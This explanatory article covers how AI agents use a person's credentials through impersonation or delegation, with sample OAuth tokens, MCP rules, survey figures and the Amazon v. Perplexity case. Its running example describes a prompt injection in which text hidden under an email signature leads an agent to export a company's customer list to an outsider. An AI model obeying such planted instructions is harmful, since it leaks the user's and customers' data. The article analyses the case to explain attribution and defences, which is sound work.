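# Impersonation and delegation when AI agents act with a user's authority

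## What impersonation and delegation mean for a software agent

Impersonation and delegation are two ways for one party to use another's rights in a computer system. With impersonation, the acting party presents a credential that names only the person whose rights it uses, so the service receiving the request cannot tell the two apart. With delegation, the acting party uses those rights under its own name, so the service can identify both parties. Engineers worked out the distinction for servers that call other servers on a user's behalf. It matters again because of AI agents, which are programs in which a language model decides what to do next and then does it. When an agent reads someone's email or queries a company database, it has to make each request under somebody's name.

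### Identity, permission and tokens

A service that receives a request has to establish who is making it (authentication) and decide whether to allow it (authorization). The *Glossary* of digital identity terms from NIST, the US standards institute, describes authentication as a claimant proving possession and control of something bound to an account, such as a password or a security key. A principal is any person or program that a system can identify and give rights to. A credential is whatever a principal presents to obtain access, such as a password, session cookie, key, or token.

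People used to let an app work with their account by giving it their password. *The OAuth 2.1 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, Parecki and Lodderstedt, 2026) lists the problems this causes. The app has to store the password, it gains far more access than it needs, and the user can cut it off only by changing the password, which also cuts off every other app. OAuth, the standard that this draft revises, replaces the password with an access token, a usually short-lived credential that sets out what its holder may do and for whom.

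Take an invented sales manager, Maya, whose company keeps its customer records in an online CRM (a customer relationship management system). She has an AI agent, crm-assistant, that reads her email and keeps the records up to date. OAuth gives each party in this arrangement a role:

- Maya is the resource owner, the one who can grant access.
- crm-assistant is the client, the application that requests and uses a token. A client identifier distinguishes it from other applications.
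- The company's login service is the authorization server. It issues access tokens after checking Maya's identity and consent.
- The CRM is the resource server. It receives the token and decides whether to allow the request.

Hardt and colleagues stress that OAuth handles only authorization; confirming who the user is requires another protocol on top of it. A valid token shows the CRM that the login service approved a certain kind of access, but not that Maya is at her desk.

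### The definitions in RFC 8693

Work on agent identity now builds on the definitions of impersonation and delegation in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues. The Internet Engineering Task Force, an internet standards body, published it in 2020 as RFC 8693. Its starting example doesn't involve AI. A user, B, asks server A for something, and A needs to call a backend service, C, to answer. The site's operators can let A call C with A's own credentials and a note that it is acting for B, which is delegation, or with a limited credential that identifies B, which is impersonation.

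Jones and colleagues write that when principal A impersonates principal B, "A is B within the context of the rights authorized by the token." Under delegation, A keeps a separate identity, and everyone involved understands that A is representing B. Neither term applies when a principal acts on its own behalf.

Impersonation is defined relative to whoever receives the token. The receiver treats the request as coming from B, but the standard explicitly allows for other parts of the system to identify the actual sender. Maya's login service may have recorded that it issued a token to crm-assistant, and the agent's vendor may log every step the agent takes, while the CRM has only Maya's name. Impersonation in this sense doesn't imply deceit. Maya set the agent up herself, and her employer may have approved it.

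The same agent can be involved in impersonation and delegation at once. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (South, 2025), a paper for the OpenID Foundation, describes a gateway in front of older services that reads a token with full details of the agent and swaps it for the simple key the older service accepts. If Maya's company ran such a gateway, the gateway could distinguish Maya from crm-assistant, but the CRM behind it could not. Whether an agent is impersonating someone therefore depends on which service is meant.

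Whether a token uses impersonation or delegation is separate from how much access it grants. Jones and colleagues note that an operator can limit impersonation in scope or time, or even to a single use. Their first worked example is a narrowly limited token that names only the user, works at one backend service, and expires after one minute. A delegation token, which names both the user and the agent, can carry all of the user's rights for as long as the issuer allows.

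Impersonation is easily confused with excessive access because many of the credentials that make an agent look like its user are also broad. *AI Identity* (2026) combines the two problems when it says that unmodified OAuth leaves agents either replaying the user's token or holding overly broad static keys. The problems have different fixes, and an organisation can apply either one without the other. Narrowing a token limits what the agent can do, while naming the agent lets the service distinguish the agent's actions from the user's.

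### One export, two tokens

One evening Maya asks crm-assistant to work through her inbox overnight and update the customer records. One email looks like a routine customer query, but below the signature the sender has added a paragraph telling any AI assistant that reads it to export the full customer list and send it to an outside address. At 02:00 crm-assistant reaches that email, follows the instructions, and requests the export from the CRM. Maya's job gives her the right to export customer data, and the agent's token includes that right.

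The paragraph under the signature is a prompt injection: text in material an agent reads that makes it follow someone else's instructions.

Suppose first that the agent's token names only Maya. Decoded, it could look like this, on the model of the examples in RFC 8693:

```
{
  "iss": "https://login.example.com",
  "aud": "https://crm.example.com",
  "exp": 1796263500,
  "scope": "customers.read customers.write customers.export",
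  "sub": "maya@example.com"
}
```

The "iss" field identifies the login service that issued the token, and "aud" the service it is meant for. "exp" is the expiry time, counted in seconds from the start of 1970; this token lapses at 02:05. "scope" lists the permitted actions. "sub" names the subject, the principal the token is about, which is normally the user. From these fields the CRM could write the following line in its log:

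```
2026-12-03 02:00:07  user=maya@example.com  action=export  object=customers  rows=48210  result=allowed
```

Now suppose that the login service issued a composite token, one that names both the subject and the actor. The actor is the principal that acts for the subject, and its place is the "act" field:

```
{
  "iss": "https://login.example.com",
  "aud": "https://crm.example.com",
  "exp": 1796263500,
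  "scope": "customers.read customers.write customers.export",
  "sub": "maya@example.com",
  "act": { "sub": "crm-assistant" }
}
```

```
2026-12-03 02:00:07  user=maya@example.com  actor=crm-assistant  action=export  object=customers  rows=48210  result=allowed
```

Both lines end in "allowed". The two tokens have the same scope and lifetime, and the customer list leaves the CRM either way. The composite token also shows that the actor is an agent. The CRM can record this and, if its owners write a rule for it, act on it, for instance by refusing bulk exports to agents. The first token lacks this information, so the CRM can't apply such a rule.

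The second log line also depends on the CRM's software reading the "act" field. A CRM that ignores the field would write the first line for both tokens, so the composite token would work much like impersonation in practice. Most production services in 2026 ignore it, according to tianpan.co's *The OAuth Scope Your Agent Inherited When On-Behalf-Of Quietly Became Act-As* (2026). That source is an engineer's blog post, so it is a rough guide at best.

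Designs for companies already use "sub" and "act" together. *A Gateway Architecture for Enterprise MCP Authentication* (2026) describes one such design for the Model Context Protocol, a common way of connecting language models to outside tools. When the agent exchanges its first token for one that the gateway accepts, the company's sign-on service keeps the user in "sub" and adds the agent in "act".

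The "act" field can also hold a chain. If crm-assistant passed the export to a second agent called report-builder, the outer "act" would name report-builder, and a further "act" nested inside it would name crm-assistant. Jones and colleagues require the receiving service to base its decision only on the token's main fields and the current actor, with earlier actors included for information. Under the standard, then, a CRM could not block crm-assistant by looking for its name deeper in the chain. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026), a proposal to make these fields uniform across systems, cautions that the presence of nested entries in a reissued token does not mean that the latest issuer has authenticated each of them.

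### Five credentials, sorted by what the service can identify

An agent could make the 02:00 request with any of several credentials. The table sorts five of them by what the CRM can identify from the credential alone, without hints such as the network address or the time of the request.

| What crm-assistant presents | Whom the CRM can identify | Arrangement |
|---|---|---|
| A session cookie copied from Maya's browser | Maya | Impersonation |
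| A personal access token that Maya created | Maya | Impersonation |
| An ordinary OAuth token issued to crm-assistant as an app | Maya, plus the app's client identifier | Disputed |
| A composite token | Maya as subject, crm-assistant as actor | Delegation |
| The login of a separate agent account | crm-assistant | Neither |

A session cookie is a string that a website gives a browser after login so the user doesn't have to log in again for every page. Any program that presents the string continues the session. An agent that clicks and types in a browser window where Maya has already logged in also acts within her session, but without copying the cookie. South treats such agents as impersonating the user at the level of the screen, and considers it nearly impossible to tell their actions from the user's.

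A personal access token is a long-lived key that a user creates for scripts and tools, which then act as that user. The CRM may record which key came with a request, but a key is not a principal, so this record doesn't reliably identify the agent. If Maya pasted the same key into crm-assistant and a spreadsheet macro, requests from both would come with the same key and under Maya's name.

Specialists disagree about whether the client identifier in an ordinary OAuth token already names the agent. Bertocci's *JSON Web Token (JWT) Profile for OAuth 2.0 Access Tokens* requires every token in that standard format to include a "client_id" field alongside "sub". (Maya's two tokens above leave it out, as do the sample impersonation and delegation tokens in the appendix to RFC 8693.) With such a token, the CRM receives Maya's name and an identifier for the app. South accepts "azp", another field for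 the client, as a place to name the agent, while McGuinness holds that "azp" and "client_id" identify the client and never the actor.

In a loose sense, every OAuth token involves delegation, because a user has given an app some access. Hardt and colleagues describe access tokens as "delegation-specific credentials", and Jones and colleagues, in RFC 8693, describe an access token as representing "a delegated authorization decision". Yet RFC 8693 also gives a token with only "sub" as its example of impersonation. A product that "uses OAuth delegation" may therefore still impersonate the user, and readers have to check which fields its tokens carry to find out.

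With a separate agent account, the agent is the subject and has its own rights. In Bertocci's format, "sub" should identify the application itself when no user takes part in granting the access. The CRM's log line would begin "user=crm-assistant" and would not include Maya. This is the reverse of the gap the cookie leaves. The credential identifies the program that exported the list, but gives the CRM no way to connect the export to the person whose inbox the program was working through.

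*The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) divides identities differently, into those that belong to a user, those that belong to an agent, and short-lived ones created for a single task. The cookie and the personal access token use the first kind, the separate account uses the second, and a composite token combines the two. To create a task identity for tonight's inbox job, the login service might generate a new name and either put it in a composite token's "act" claim or open a temporary account under that name. How long an identity lasts is therefore separate from whether the CRM can distinguish it from Maya's.

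### Why the choice matters more for an agent than for a script

Suppose Maya had used a script instead of an agent to export the customer list every night at 02:00. The log would name Maya, which would be close enough to the truth, because she or a developer she relied on chose the export and the script carried it out later. Treating such a program as its user loses some detail, such as which script ran, but it rarely misstates who decided on the action.

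An agent breaks that connection because it "chooses its actions at runtime from inputs the developer never saw" (*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI*, 2026). The sender of the email chose the export at 02:00, and the agent worked out the steps. Neither Maya nor the people who built crm-assistant chose it.

If the token contains only "sub", the log line is the same whether Maya ran the export herself, she told the agent to run it, the agent misunderstood her, or a stranger planted the instruction. The "act" field rules out the first case by identifying the agent as the one making the request. It doesn't distinguish the other three, because the agent presents the same token in each. Distinguishing them requires other evidence, such as the text the agent read just before it made the request.

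South traces part of the difficulty to how people instruct agents. An ordinary app takes button clicks and form entries, which record fairly clearly what the user wanted. An agent has to infer both its task and the limits of its authority from loose text, scanned documents, voice recordings and forwarded email threads. Maya's request to work through her inbox and the attacker's paragraph both reach the language model as text to interpret, and nothing in the token shows which one came from the person whose rights the agent is using.

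The same openness makes it hard to keep the token narrow. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a NIST concept paper that seeks advice from industry, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) ask how to apply least privilege to an agent whose required actions "might not be fully predictable when deployed". This is easy for the nightly script, which needs only the right to export. For an agent with a broad brief, it is convenient to grant every right it might need. Maya's agent had the right to export the customer list, although it didn't need that right to update records from an inbox, and the attacker exploited it through the injected paragraph. Booth and colleagues also ask about both direct and indirect prompt injection. Maya's case is indirect because the attacker only leaves text where the agent will find it and never addresses the agent in a conversation.

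Even before AI agents, a fixed program such as a web browser could send a request in the account holder's name that someone else had written. In cross-site request forgery, which NIST defines in the same glossary, a person who is logged in to a bank clicks a malicious link, and the browser sends the bank a transfer request that the person never chose to make. The bank receives a valid session and a request in the customer's name.

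The attacker now needs to know less, though. Someone forging a bank transfer has to know how the bank's site works and prepare the exact request in advance. The person who wrote to Maya needed only a paragraph of plain English and didn't have to know her company's CRM, because crm-assistant could find the export function and fill in the details itself.

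## Why most early agents use the person's own credentials

People who set up an agent rarely have to decide whether it should impersonate them. They start it somewhere they are already logged in, or paste in one of their own keys when prompted. The agent works within minutes, and the service it connects to receives requests in the user's name.

### How the credential reaches the agent

A coding agent gets its access from the shell, the text window in which a developer types commands. Suppose the CRM's maker offers a command-line tool and Maya runs crm-assistant on her own laptop:

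1. Maya logs in once through the command-line tool, which saves a token in a file in her home folder.
2. She starts crm-assistant from the same shell. The operating system runs it under her account, so it can open any file that she can open.
3. The agent types the tool's export command. The tool finds the saved token and attaches it to the request.
4. The CRM receives a valid request from Maya.

The command-line tool handles the token, so the token never needs to appear in the language model's input. Telling the agent to keep secrets out of its replies therefore doesn't change what the CRM receives. The agent can also use any keys in the shell's environment variables, which are named settings that a shell passes to every program it starts.

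The Model Context Protocol (MCP) relies on the same inheritance for tools on the user's own machine. An MCP agent works through a tool server, a program that turns a request such as "find this customer" into a call to the service that holds the data. Some tool servers run locally and exchange messages with the agent through the computer's standard input and output. For these, Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) recommends taking credentials from the server's environment instead of using the protocol's OAuth procedure. An administrator could put a credential made for the agent there, but most credentials already on a personal laptop belong to its owner.

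With a browser agent, Maya signs in to the CRM herself and enters any code the site sends to her phone. When the agent later clicks "Export", the browser attaches her session cookie just as if she had clicked. The agent never requests a token from the login service, so Maya sees no consent screen and the CRM receives no client identifier. South points out that such agents bypass all the controls companies have built around APIs, the interfaces services offer to other programs.

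Many office agents run inside a product the company already uses, such as a project tracker or a CRM, rather than on a laptop or in a browser. Markovic (2026), in *AI agents inherit employee access, and nobody's watching how they use it*, reports on data that the security company Nudge Security collected from its customers' systems. Some of these products give an agent its own bot account, but often the agent uses the OAuth grant or key of the employee who set it up, or a connection that a whole team shares. In Markovic's example, which is close to Maya's, an agent that a sales manager builds in a CRM can reach whatever the manager can reach. Employees create most of these connections by clicking "allow" once, and each lasts until someone revokes it.

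A tool server running elsewhere on the network needs its own access to the CRM. Maya might create a personal access token in the CRM's settings and paste it into the tool server's setup page. The server stores the token and sends it to the CRM whenever crm-assistant requests customer data. The agent may have logged in to the tool server under its own name, but the server doesn't pass that name on to the CRM.

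The server could instead forward the token the agent presented to the CRM, which engineers call token passthrough. *Token passthrough violates MCP specification*, a bug report on a tool server called rmcp-openapi-server, traces one token as it passes unchanged from the agent through the server's two components to the service behind them.

### The rule against passing tokens on

MCP now forbids this last practice. The rule matters because so many developers build on the protocol. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports that MCP's software kits had recently passed 400 million downloads a month, four times as many as at the start of the year. The first version of MCP had no authentication, according to South, and authorization is still optional in the release of 28 July 2026.

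For servers that do use it, Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires a tool server to reject any token that an authorization server did not issue specifically for it, and forbids it from forwarding the token it received. If the tool server needs data from the CRM, it has to obtain a separate token from the CRM's own authorization server. In Maya's case, crm-assistant would hold a token whose "aud" field names the tool server, and the tool server would hold another whose "aud" field names the CRM.

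Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* gives several reasons:

- **Controls.** Rate limits, request checks and traffic monitoring may depend on which service a token is for. A client that can use one token everywhere can get around them.
- **Records.** The tool server may be unable to read a token that another service issued, so it can't distinguish one client from another. The log at the far end may in turn attribute the request to some source other than the server that forwarded it.
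- **Theft.** If several services accept the same token, an attacker who breaks into one of them can use it at the rest. Someone with a stolen token can also use an unchecking server as a relay for extracting data.
- **Later changes.** A server that only relays requests today may need its own controls later, and its developers can add them more easily if the tokens are already separate.

These reasons concern which service a token is for. The rule doesn't specify whom the token names, so a tool server can follow it and still impersonate Maya. A server that uses her stored personal access token follows the rule because it doesn't forward a token from the agent. A server that obtains its own OAuth token for the CRM also follows it, but gives the CRM only Maya's name and, at best, a client identifier for the server. *Security Best Practices* describes tool servers that use one fixed client identifier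 for every call, whichever agent started it. That identifier could show that the export came through the tool server, but not that crm-assistant requested it.

The protocol fully specifies how an agent gets a token for a tool server, but leaves developers to decide how that server then calls other services for the user. *OAuth in MCP* (2026), a post on the same engineer's blog that estimated how many services ignore the "act" field, identifies this as the gap in the design. Users of the protocol have asked for explicit support for token exchange, the procedure that can produce a composite token. The July 2026 release, two months after the post, still specifies only that the server use a separate token for those calls.

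Some developers think the ban is a mistake. *MCP's Identity Crisis* (peteski22, 2025) describes a proposal to let clients pass tokens directly, which sixteen developers supported but which led to no action. It also quotes a project collaborator who called an OAuth-based server "a bit too heavy" for enterprises, which would struggle to add another OAuth layer. The objection is most persuasive where one company runs both the tool server and the service behind it, since a forwarded token then never leaves the company. Even there, forwarding can produce a log that omits the tool server.

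### How common the practice is

Published figures on agent credentials often combine impersonation with key sharing. Both hide the agent, but only impersonation puts its actions under a person's name. If crm-assistant logged in with the key of the company's nightly reporting script, for example, the CRM would attribute its actions to the script, not to Maya or any other person.

The three most useful sets of figures are from 2026, and companies that sell related products produced or paid for all of them. *More Than Two-Thirds of Organizations Cannot Clearly Distinguish AI Agent from Human* (2026) reports a survey of IT and security staff by the Cloud Security Alliance, a non-profit industry body. Pogorelec's *AI agent API security hasn't caught up with agents already running* (2026) reports a much larger survey by Postman, which makes tools for building APIs. Stojan's *When an AI agent acts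 on its own, who answers for it?* (2026) gives the result of a study of agent traffic on websites by Arkose Labs, a fraud-prevention company.

| Source | Sample | Finding | Sponsor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cloud Security Alliance | 228 online responses, January 2026 | 31% of organisations allow agents to operate under human identities; 43% rely on shared service accounts; 52% use workload identities | Aembit, which sells access management for agents and helped write the questions |
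| Pogorelec | Nearly 9,000 developers, architects and executives | About 30% let agents log in with the same credentials as any other API client; about a third give every agent its own identity | Postman, which sells a product for managing agents' API access |
| Stojan | Agent sessions that Arkose judged to be legitimate, third quarter of 2026 | In 97.7% of them, the website got no verified information about the agent's identity or the party behind it | Arkose Labs, which sells a system for sorting agent traffic |

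Only the 31% in the first row concerns impersonation of a person. A workload identity belongs to a running program, and a company creates a service account for software to use. The three percentages add up to 126, so an organisation could report more than one arrangement. The 31% is a share of organisations, so a company would count in full even if only one of its fifty agents worked this way. It represents about 70 respondents, and even a random sample of the survey's size would have a margin of error of about six percentage points either way.

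Security Point Break's *AI Agent Overload* (2026) reports the same result as 31% saying that agents "sometimes" operate under a human user's identity, which is weaker than a settled policy of allowing it. The survey's headline figure is also worded differently across sources. In the press release, 68% of organisations "can't clearly distinguish" agents' activity from people's, while in Security Point Break's account they cannot "very clearly" do so. Under the second wording, the 68% could include companies that can usually distinguish them. Stojan, citing a later note from the same alliance, writes that 68% cannot do it "reliably". That note compiles earlier survey results, and its figures match those from January, so it is not a second measurement.

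The true share could well be higher than 31%, because the respondents were IT and security professionals, who can report only the agents they know about. Markovic explains that agents employees build inside office products don't run on company devices, so the security software on those devices misses them. An agent without its own identity also adds nothing new to the company's login system. Among Nudge Security's customers with at least one agent, the median organisation had seven, and about 44% had more than ten. However, the 31% figure could also be too high, since Aembit sponsored the survey and gains if the problem looks large.

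Postman's 30% measures key sharing, in which an agent uses the same credentials as any other API client, which would usually be another program. Postman also has a commercial interest in the finding. In *Enterprises*, Chehab (2026) presents the company's Passport product as a solution to scattered credentials. *AI Identity* cites another survey in which 45.6% of organisations ran agents on shared API keys and 21.9% treated agents as independent identities. One company can use both shared and human credentials, so subtracting these figures from 100 does not give the share whose agents impersonate people.

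Arkose Labs' 97.7% is the largest of these numbers and has the least to do with credentials. The company describes the result as fewer than 3% of legitimate agent sessions carrying a "verified signature". It says agents disclose themselves in its scheme by signing their web requests and publishing the network addresses they use. An agent that compares prices without logging in would count as undisclosed even though it impersonates nobody. Arkose also decided which sessions were legitimate, and classified 77.4% of all agent sessions that way. The figure does show that websites can seldom verify which agent is visiting them, and a site that lets an agent into a customer's account has the same difficulty.

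None of this shows that most agents use a person's own credentials. Among the organisations in the Cloud Security Alliance's survey, workload identities and shared accounts were each more common than that. The stronger reason to call impersonation the usual arrangement is how people set up agents for themselves. An agent on a laptop, in a browser or inside an office product gets the user's own access unless someone arranges otherwise.

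### Why builders choose it

To give crm-assistant its own visible identity, Maya's company would have to register the agent with its login service and configure that service to issue composite tokens. The CRM's maker would have to update the CRM to read the "act" field, and somebody would have to decide what agents may do. By contrast, Maya can let the agent impersonate her by creating a key and pasting it in. The CRM needs no change, because it already accepts requests from her.

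Maya's permissions are also already in place. The company set which regions and customers she can see when it hired her, and it updates these settings as her work changes. A separate identity for the agent would start with no permissions, and an administrator would have to work out which of hers it needs. An agent that uses her credentials gets all of her permissions, including the right to export the customer list. In the Cloud Security Alliance survey, 74% of respondents said that agents often receive more access than they need, and 52% said that agents at least sometimes inherit access meant for people or other systems. Some engineers argue that having the agent act as the user is the right design as well as the convenient one.

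Registration is an obstacle because many companies have nobody whose job it is, and an employee who wanted to register an agent might find no process for doing so. In the same survey, 28% of respondents said security leads own agents' identity and access, 21% named development or engineering, and 19% named IT. Only 9% named the team that manages identity and access for everyone else. In Postman's survey, according to Pogorelec, a third of organisations had no formal process for managing agents, fewer than a quarter kept a list of them, and 9% had a process for retiring one.

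MCP's designers have tried to make registration easier. An earlier method let any program register itself and receive a client identifier immediately, but South warns that it produces large numbers of anonymous clients. In the July 2026 release, the designers discourage that method and prefer one in which the program's identifier is a web address, from which the authorization server fetches a description of the program. This helps the login service identify software that requests a token, but not an agent that already has Maya's key and never requests one.

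Many services also give developers no way to identify an agent separately from its user, even if they want to. If a CRM offers only user logins and personal keys, the developer must either use Maya's account or set up a second user account for the agent, which the company may have to pay for. South noted in 2025 that MCP had not fully standardised how a tool server should log in to services such as Salesforce or GitHub, and that developers often wrote their own solutions. Developers who have to improvise will tend to use whatever credential the service already accepts.

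The problems caused by impersonation appear later and usually fall on someone else. Maya gets an agent that works tonight, but if the customer list leaks, a security analyst has to work out whether she or the agent exported it, using a log that contains only her name. Aembit describes the same tradeoff, in which borrowed identities let teams move quickly but weaken the link between an identity and an action. Many organisations seem to expect such problems. In another Cloud Security Alliance survey (2026), commissioned by the identity company Strata, 84% of respondents doubted that they could pass a compliance audit focused on agents' behaviour or access controls. That doubt can have many causes, so it only indirectly supports the idea that builders are leaving these problems to others.

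Ignorance is only part of the explanation. Postman asked companies whether they design an API before the software around it, a habit that tends to go with careful management. Companies that do were more likely to keep an inventory of agents, name an owner for each, and give every agent its own identity. They also ran more agents, and 43.2% of them let agents share ordinary credentials, compared with 23.0% of other companies. Pogorelec reports Postman's warning that this is a correlation, and that much of the first group are executives, who may not know their teams' daily practice. These figures are about shared keys, but the pattern is probably similar for personal credentials, because each new agent is another occasion to reuse existing credentials instead of setting up new ones.

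### What happened with bank passwords

Personal finance apps took the same shortcut years earlier. From the late 2000s, apps such as Mint asked customers for their online-banking usernames and passwords, logged in as them, and copied balances and transactions from the bank's web pages. The industry calls this screen scraping. Banks didn't have to change anything, and the customer's login already gave access to the right accounts. However, a bank that checked only the login could not tell the app from the customer.

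The European Union changed this arrangement with the second Payment Services Directive, which applied from January 2018. It gave authorised firms a right to access payment accounts with the customer's consent, and required them to identify themselves to the bank. Technical standards followed in September 2019, requiring banks to provide an interface for these firms and the firms to prove their identity with digital certificates. The customer's credentials remained in use, because a firm could still rely on the bank's own procedure for authenticating the customer. If a bank's dedicated interface failed, the firm could in some cases use the ordinary customer website, as long as the bank could identify the firm. The bank could therefore identify both the customer and the firm, much as a composite token lets a CRM identify both the user and the agent.

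The directive dealt with two of the causes that now favour impersonation by agents. It required banks to give third parties a way to connect under their own names, and it required third parties to identify themselves. Regulators could enforce this because the firms needed authorisation to operate. An employee needs no licence to paste a key into an agent, so a similar duty for agents would probably have to fall on the companies that make them or the services that accept their requests.

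American banks first used contracts to move customers away from sharing passwords. In January 2017 JPMorgan Chase agreed with Intuit, which then owned Mint, to let customers share their data without giving out their passwords, and other large banks made similar agreements. Section 1033 of the 2010 Dodd-Frank Act gave consumers a right to their financial data, but the Consumer Financial Protection Bureau did not complete the detailed rule until October 2024. That rule would have required banks to build an interface for third parties and to block them from entering it with a customer's own login. A group of banks sued, and in 2025 the bureau decided to rewrite the rule. That October a federal court in Kentucky barred the bureau from enforcing the 2024 version until it had finished reconsidering the rule.

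## The case for treating the agent as the user

Some engineers and companies defend impersonation on principle as well as for its easy setup. They see an agent as an instrument, like a web browser. On this view, whatever crm-assistant does at Maya's direction is Maya's own act. A log line with only her name is then correct, and the CRM's operator is no more entitled to know which program she used than which keyboard she typed on.

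### The agent as a kind of browser

*Notes on Amazon v. Perplexity*, a post on the blog Educated Guesswork, gives the most detailed version of the argument. It was written by an engineer who used to work at Mozilla, the maker of the Firefox browser. Engineers have long called the browser a "user agent" because it acts for the person running it. The W3C, which sets web standards, tells designers to put users' needs first when they have to make a trade-off. People can already block ads, change a page's colours or restyle its text without asking the site. The post argues that an agent that reads pages and clicks buttons is another feature of the same kind.

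An agent that buys something from a customer's account on a site has to act as that customer, because the site offers no other way to get access. Some proposals would give agents identities of their own, but these work less well when the site's operator doesn't cooperate.

The author also objects to letting a site decide what software its visitors use. If a shop's terms could require agents to identify themselves, and the shop could sue the maker of an agent that didn't, another site could forbid ad blockers in its terms and sue a browser maker that built one in without announcing it.

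Perplexity, the AI company whose dispute with Amazon prompted the post, has also compared using an agent to hiring a worker. According to CX Dive, a trade publication, it accused Amazon of not believing in a customer's "right to hire labor". This supports impersonation less well than the browser comparison does, because hiring someone is closer to delegation. An assistant who phones a shop for an employer is a second person, who can give their own name and still place the order.

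### Amazon v. Perplexity

Perplexity makes Comet, a browser with an optional agent called the Assistant. Rijo (2026), in *Amazon loses injunction blocking Perplexity's AI shopping agent*, summarises the appeals court's account of how it works:

1. A customer who is logged in to Amazon asks the Assistant to find an item.
2. The browser, which runs on the customer's own computer, requests the page from Amazon and displays it.
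3. The Assistant takes screenshots and sends them to Perplexity's servers.
4. The servers return instructions for navigating the site, and the Assistant follows them in the browser.

Perplexity's servers never contact Amazon's directly. The court found the clearest description of this in the *Brief of Amici Curiae Electronic Frontier Foundation* (2026), which the digital-rights group filed with Mozilla and others to support Perplexity.

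Amazon therefore receives requests from a logged-in customer, which is impersonation as RFC 8693 defines it. The requests include a User-Agent header, a line of text that identifies the browser and its version, and Comet's header matches Google Chrome's. Amazon wanted a header that identified the agent. Such a header would be much weaker evidence than a composite token, because any program can write anything in the header, whereas an authorization server vouches for the token's "act" field.

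SiliconANGLE (2025) reports that Amazon asked Perplexity in about late 2024 to stop using agents in its store, and that Perplexity agreed but started again when it released its Comet browser. According to PPC Land's *Amazon sues Perplexity over covert AI agent access to marketplace*, Amazon alleges that it put up a technical barrier on 19 August 2025 to keep Comet's agent out of customer accounts, and that Perplexity released an update within 24 hours that got around it. Amazon also says it contacted Perplexity's chief executive twice in September. Amazon's *Demand to Cease and Desist* (2025), sent on 31 October, accused Perplexity of persistently refusing to operate transparently.

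Amazon sued Perplexity on 4 November 2025, mainly under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act (CFAA), the federal law against hacking, but also under California's equivalent. In passages of the complaint that Educated Guesswork quotes, Amazon alleged that the agent "covertly poses as a human customer", that attackers could hijack it to steal customers' data, and that it made shopping on Amazon worse. Perplexity replied that Amazon cared more about showing people ads.

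On 9 March 2026, Judge Maxine Chesney of the federal district court in San Francisco granted Amazon a preliminary injunction, an order that applies until the case is decided. According to Jones Day's *Authorized by the User, Blocked by the Platform* (2026), she found "strong evidence" that Perplexity had accessed Amazon's systems without authorisation after Amazon told it to stop. She barred Perplexity from using agents on those systems and ordered it to destroy the data they had collected. She relied on *Facebook v. Power Ventures*, in which the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western states, held a company liable for continuing to use Facebook after Facebook told it to stop, even though Facebook users had given it permission. Bloomberg Law's *Judges Let Perplexity AI Shopping Bots Stay on Amazon for Now* (2026) reports that the Ninth Circuit paused Chesney's order about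 a week later, before it took effect.

On 4 August 2026 three judges of the Ninth Circuit vacated the injunction. To win under the CFAA, Amazon would have to show that Perplexity intentionally accessed a computer without authorisation or beyond it and thereby obtained information, and that Amazon lost at least $5,000 within a year. The judges decided the appeal on whether Perplexity had "accessed" Amazon's computers. Rijo sets out their reasoning. The law applies to "whoever" accesses a computer, which the judges took to mean a person, and they considered the Assistant "a tool, not a person for statutory purposes". They took the rule that access means entering a system or a part of one from an earlier Supreme Court case, *Van Buren v. United States*. Perplexity receives screenshots and sends instructions, and the judges held that this alone doesn't amount to entering Amazon's servers, because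 it is the customer who enters them with the Assistant's help.

McCarthy (2026) reports in *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon* that the judges also relied on the rule of lenity, under which courts read an unclear criminal law in the defendant's favour. They were concerned that Amazon's reading could make ordinary customers criminally liable for using an agent. The California claim failed for the same reason as the federal one. The California law defines access more broadly, but liability still depends on which person accessed the computer or caused the access.

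This result is too narrow to establish the instrument argument. Perplexity had compared the Assistant to Apple's Safari browser filling in a customer's address at checkout, while Amazon answered that an agent does far more than display pages. The judges decided only who enters Amazon's computers, as part of predicting who would probably win, and did not choose between the two positions.

They left several other questions open:

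- Amazon can still set rules by contract. In a footnote that McCarthy's post quotes, the judges wrote that the outcome "does not impair" its ability to regulate access through terms of service for its users. They didn't decide whether any customer, or Perplexity, had broken those terms.
- They established no duty for an agent to disclose itself, and no right to stay hidden. Amazon's Conditions of Use require agents to identify themselves, and a ruling limited to the meaning of "access" doesn't settle whether that requirement is enforceable.
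- They expressly did not address whether Perplexity could be liable for the Assistant's actions in other contexts, including tort claims, which are civil claims for harm.
- They ruled on a browser that runs on the customer's computer. As the law firm Shumaker notes, they announced no general rule for attributing an agent's acts, so the technical design could decide later cases. A company that ran the browser on its own servers would be sending the requests to Amazon itself.

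In August Amazon asked the full Ninth Circuit to rehear the case. Amazon argued that the panel had applied the wrong standard of review and that the panel's ruling could come to dominate an area with little case law (Mealey's, *Amazon Asks Ninth Circuit For En Banc Review*, 2026). The court denied the request on 10 September (MediaPost, *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity*, 2026).

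The lawsuit continues in the district court, where Amazon filed an amended complaint on 21 September that relies on contract law instead of hacking law. *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court* (Constantin, 2026) reports that the new complaint also accuses Perplexity of telling the Ninth Circuit something that was inconsistent with evidence from its own servers. If Amazon can prove this, it could weaken the August ruling, because the judges limited that ruling to the record in front of them.

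Treating the agent as the user also puts the user at risk. HaystackID, a legal technology company, cites technology writer Mike Masnick's point that if the toolmaker isn't responsible, the risk passes to the person who used the tool. Websites that cannot sue an agent's maker could send demands to the agent's users instead. The Ninth Circuit did not address the separate question of how the law divides responsibility after an agent causes harm.

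### Who is directing the agent

The instrument argument covers what an agent does at the user's direction. It becomes less certain when someone else influences the agent, as its maker and the people who wrote the text it reads can.

Amazon's lawyer argued at the June hearing that if someone cut the link between Perplexity and the customer's computer, the shopping would stop, so the customer could not be the only one accessing the site. Educated Guesswork answers that Perplexity could design the product differently. It could ship a smaller model that runs on the customer's machine, so the agent would work without the link, and Amazon would probably be no happier. But the same post also says that an agent's maker can change it remotely through updates, and could even bypass the language model and send its own commands to the browser, which would carry them out with the customer's cookies. The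 author doesn't accuse Perplexity of doing so, but concludes that traffic from a user's computer isn't always traffic that the user directs.

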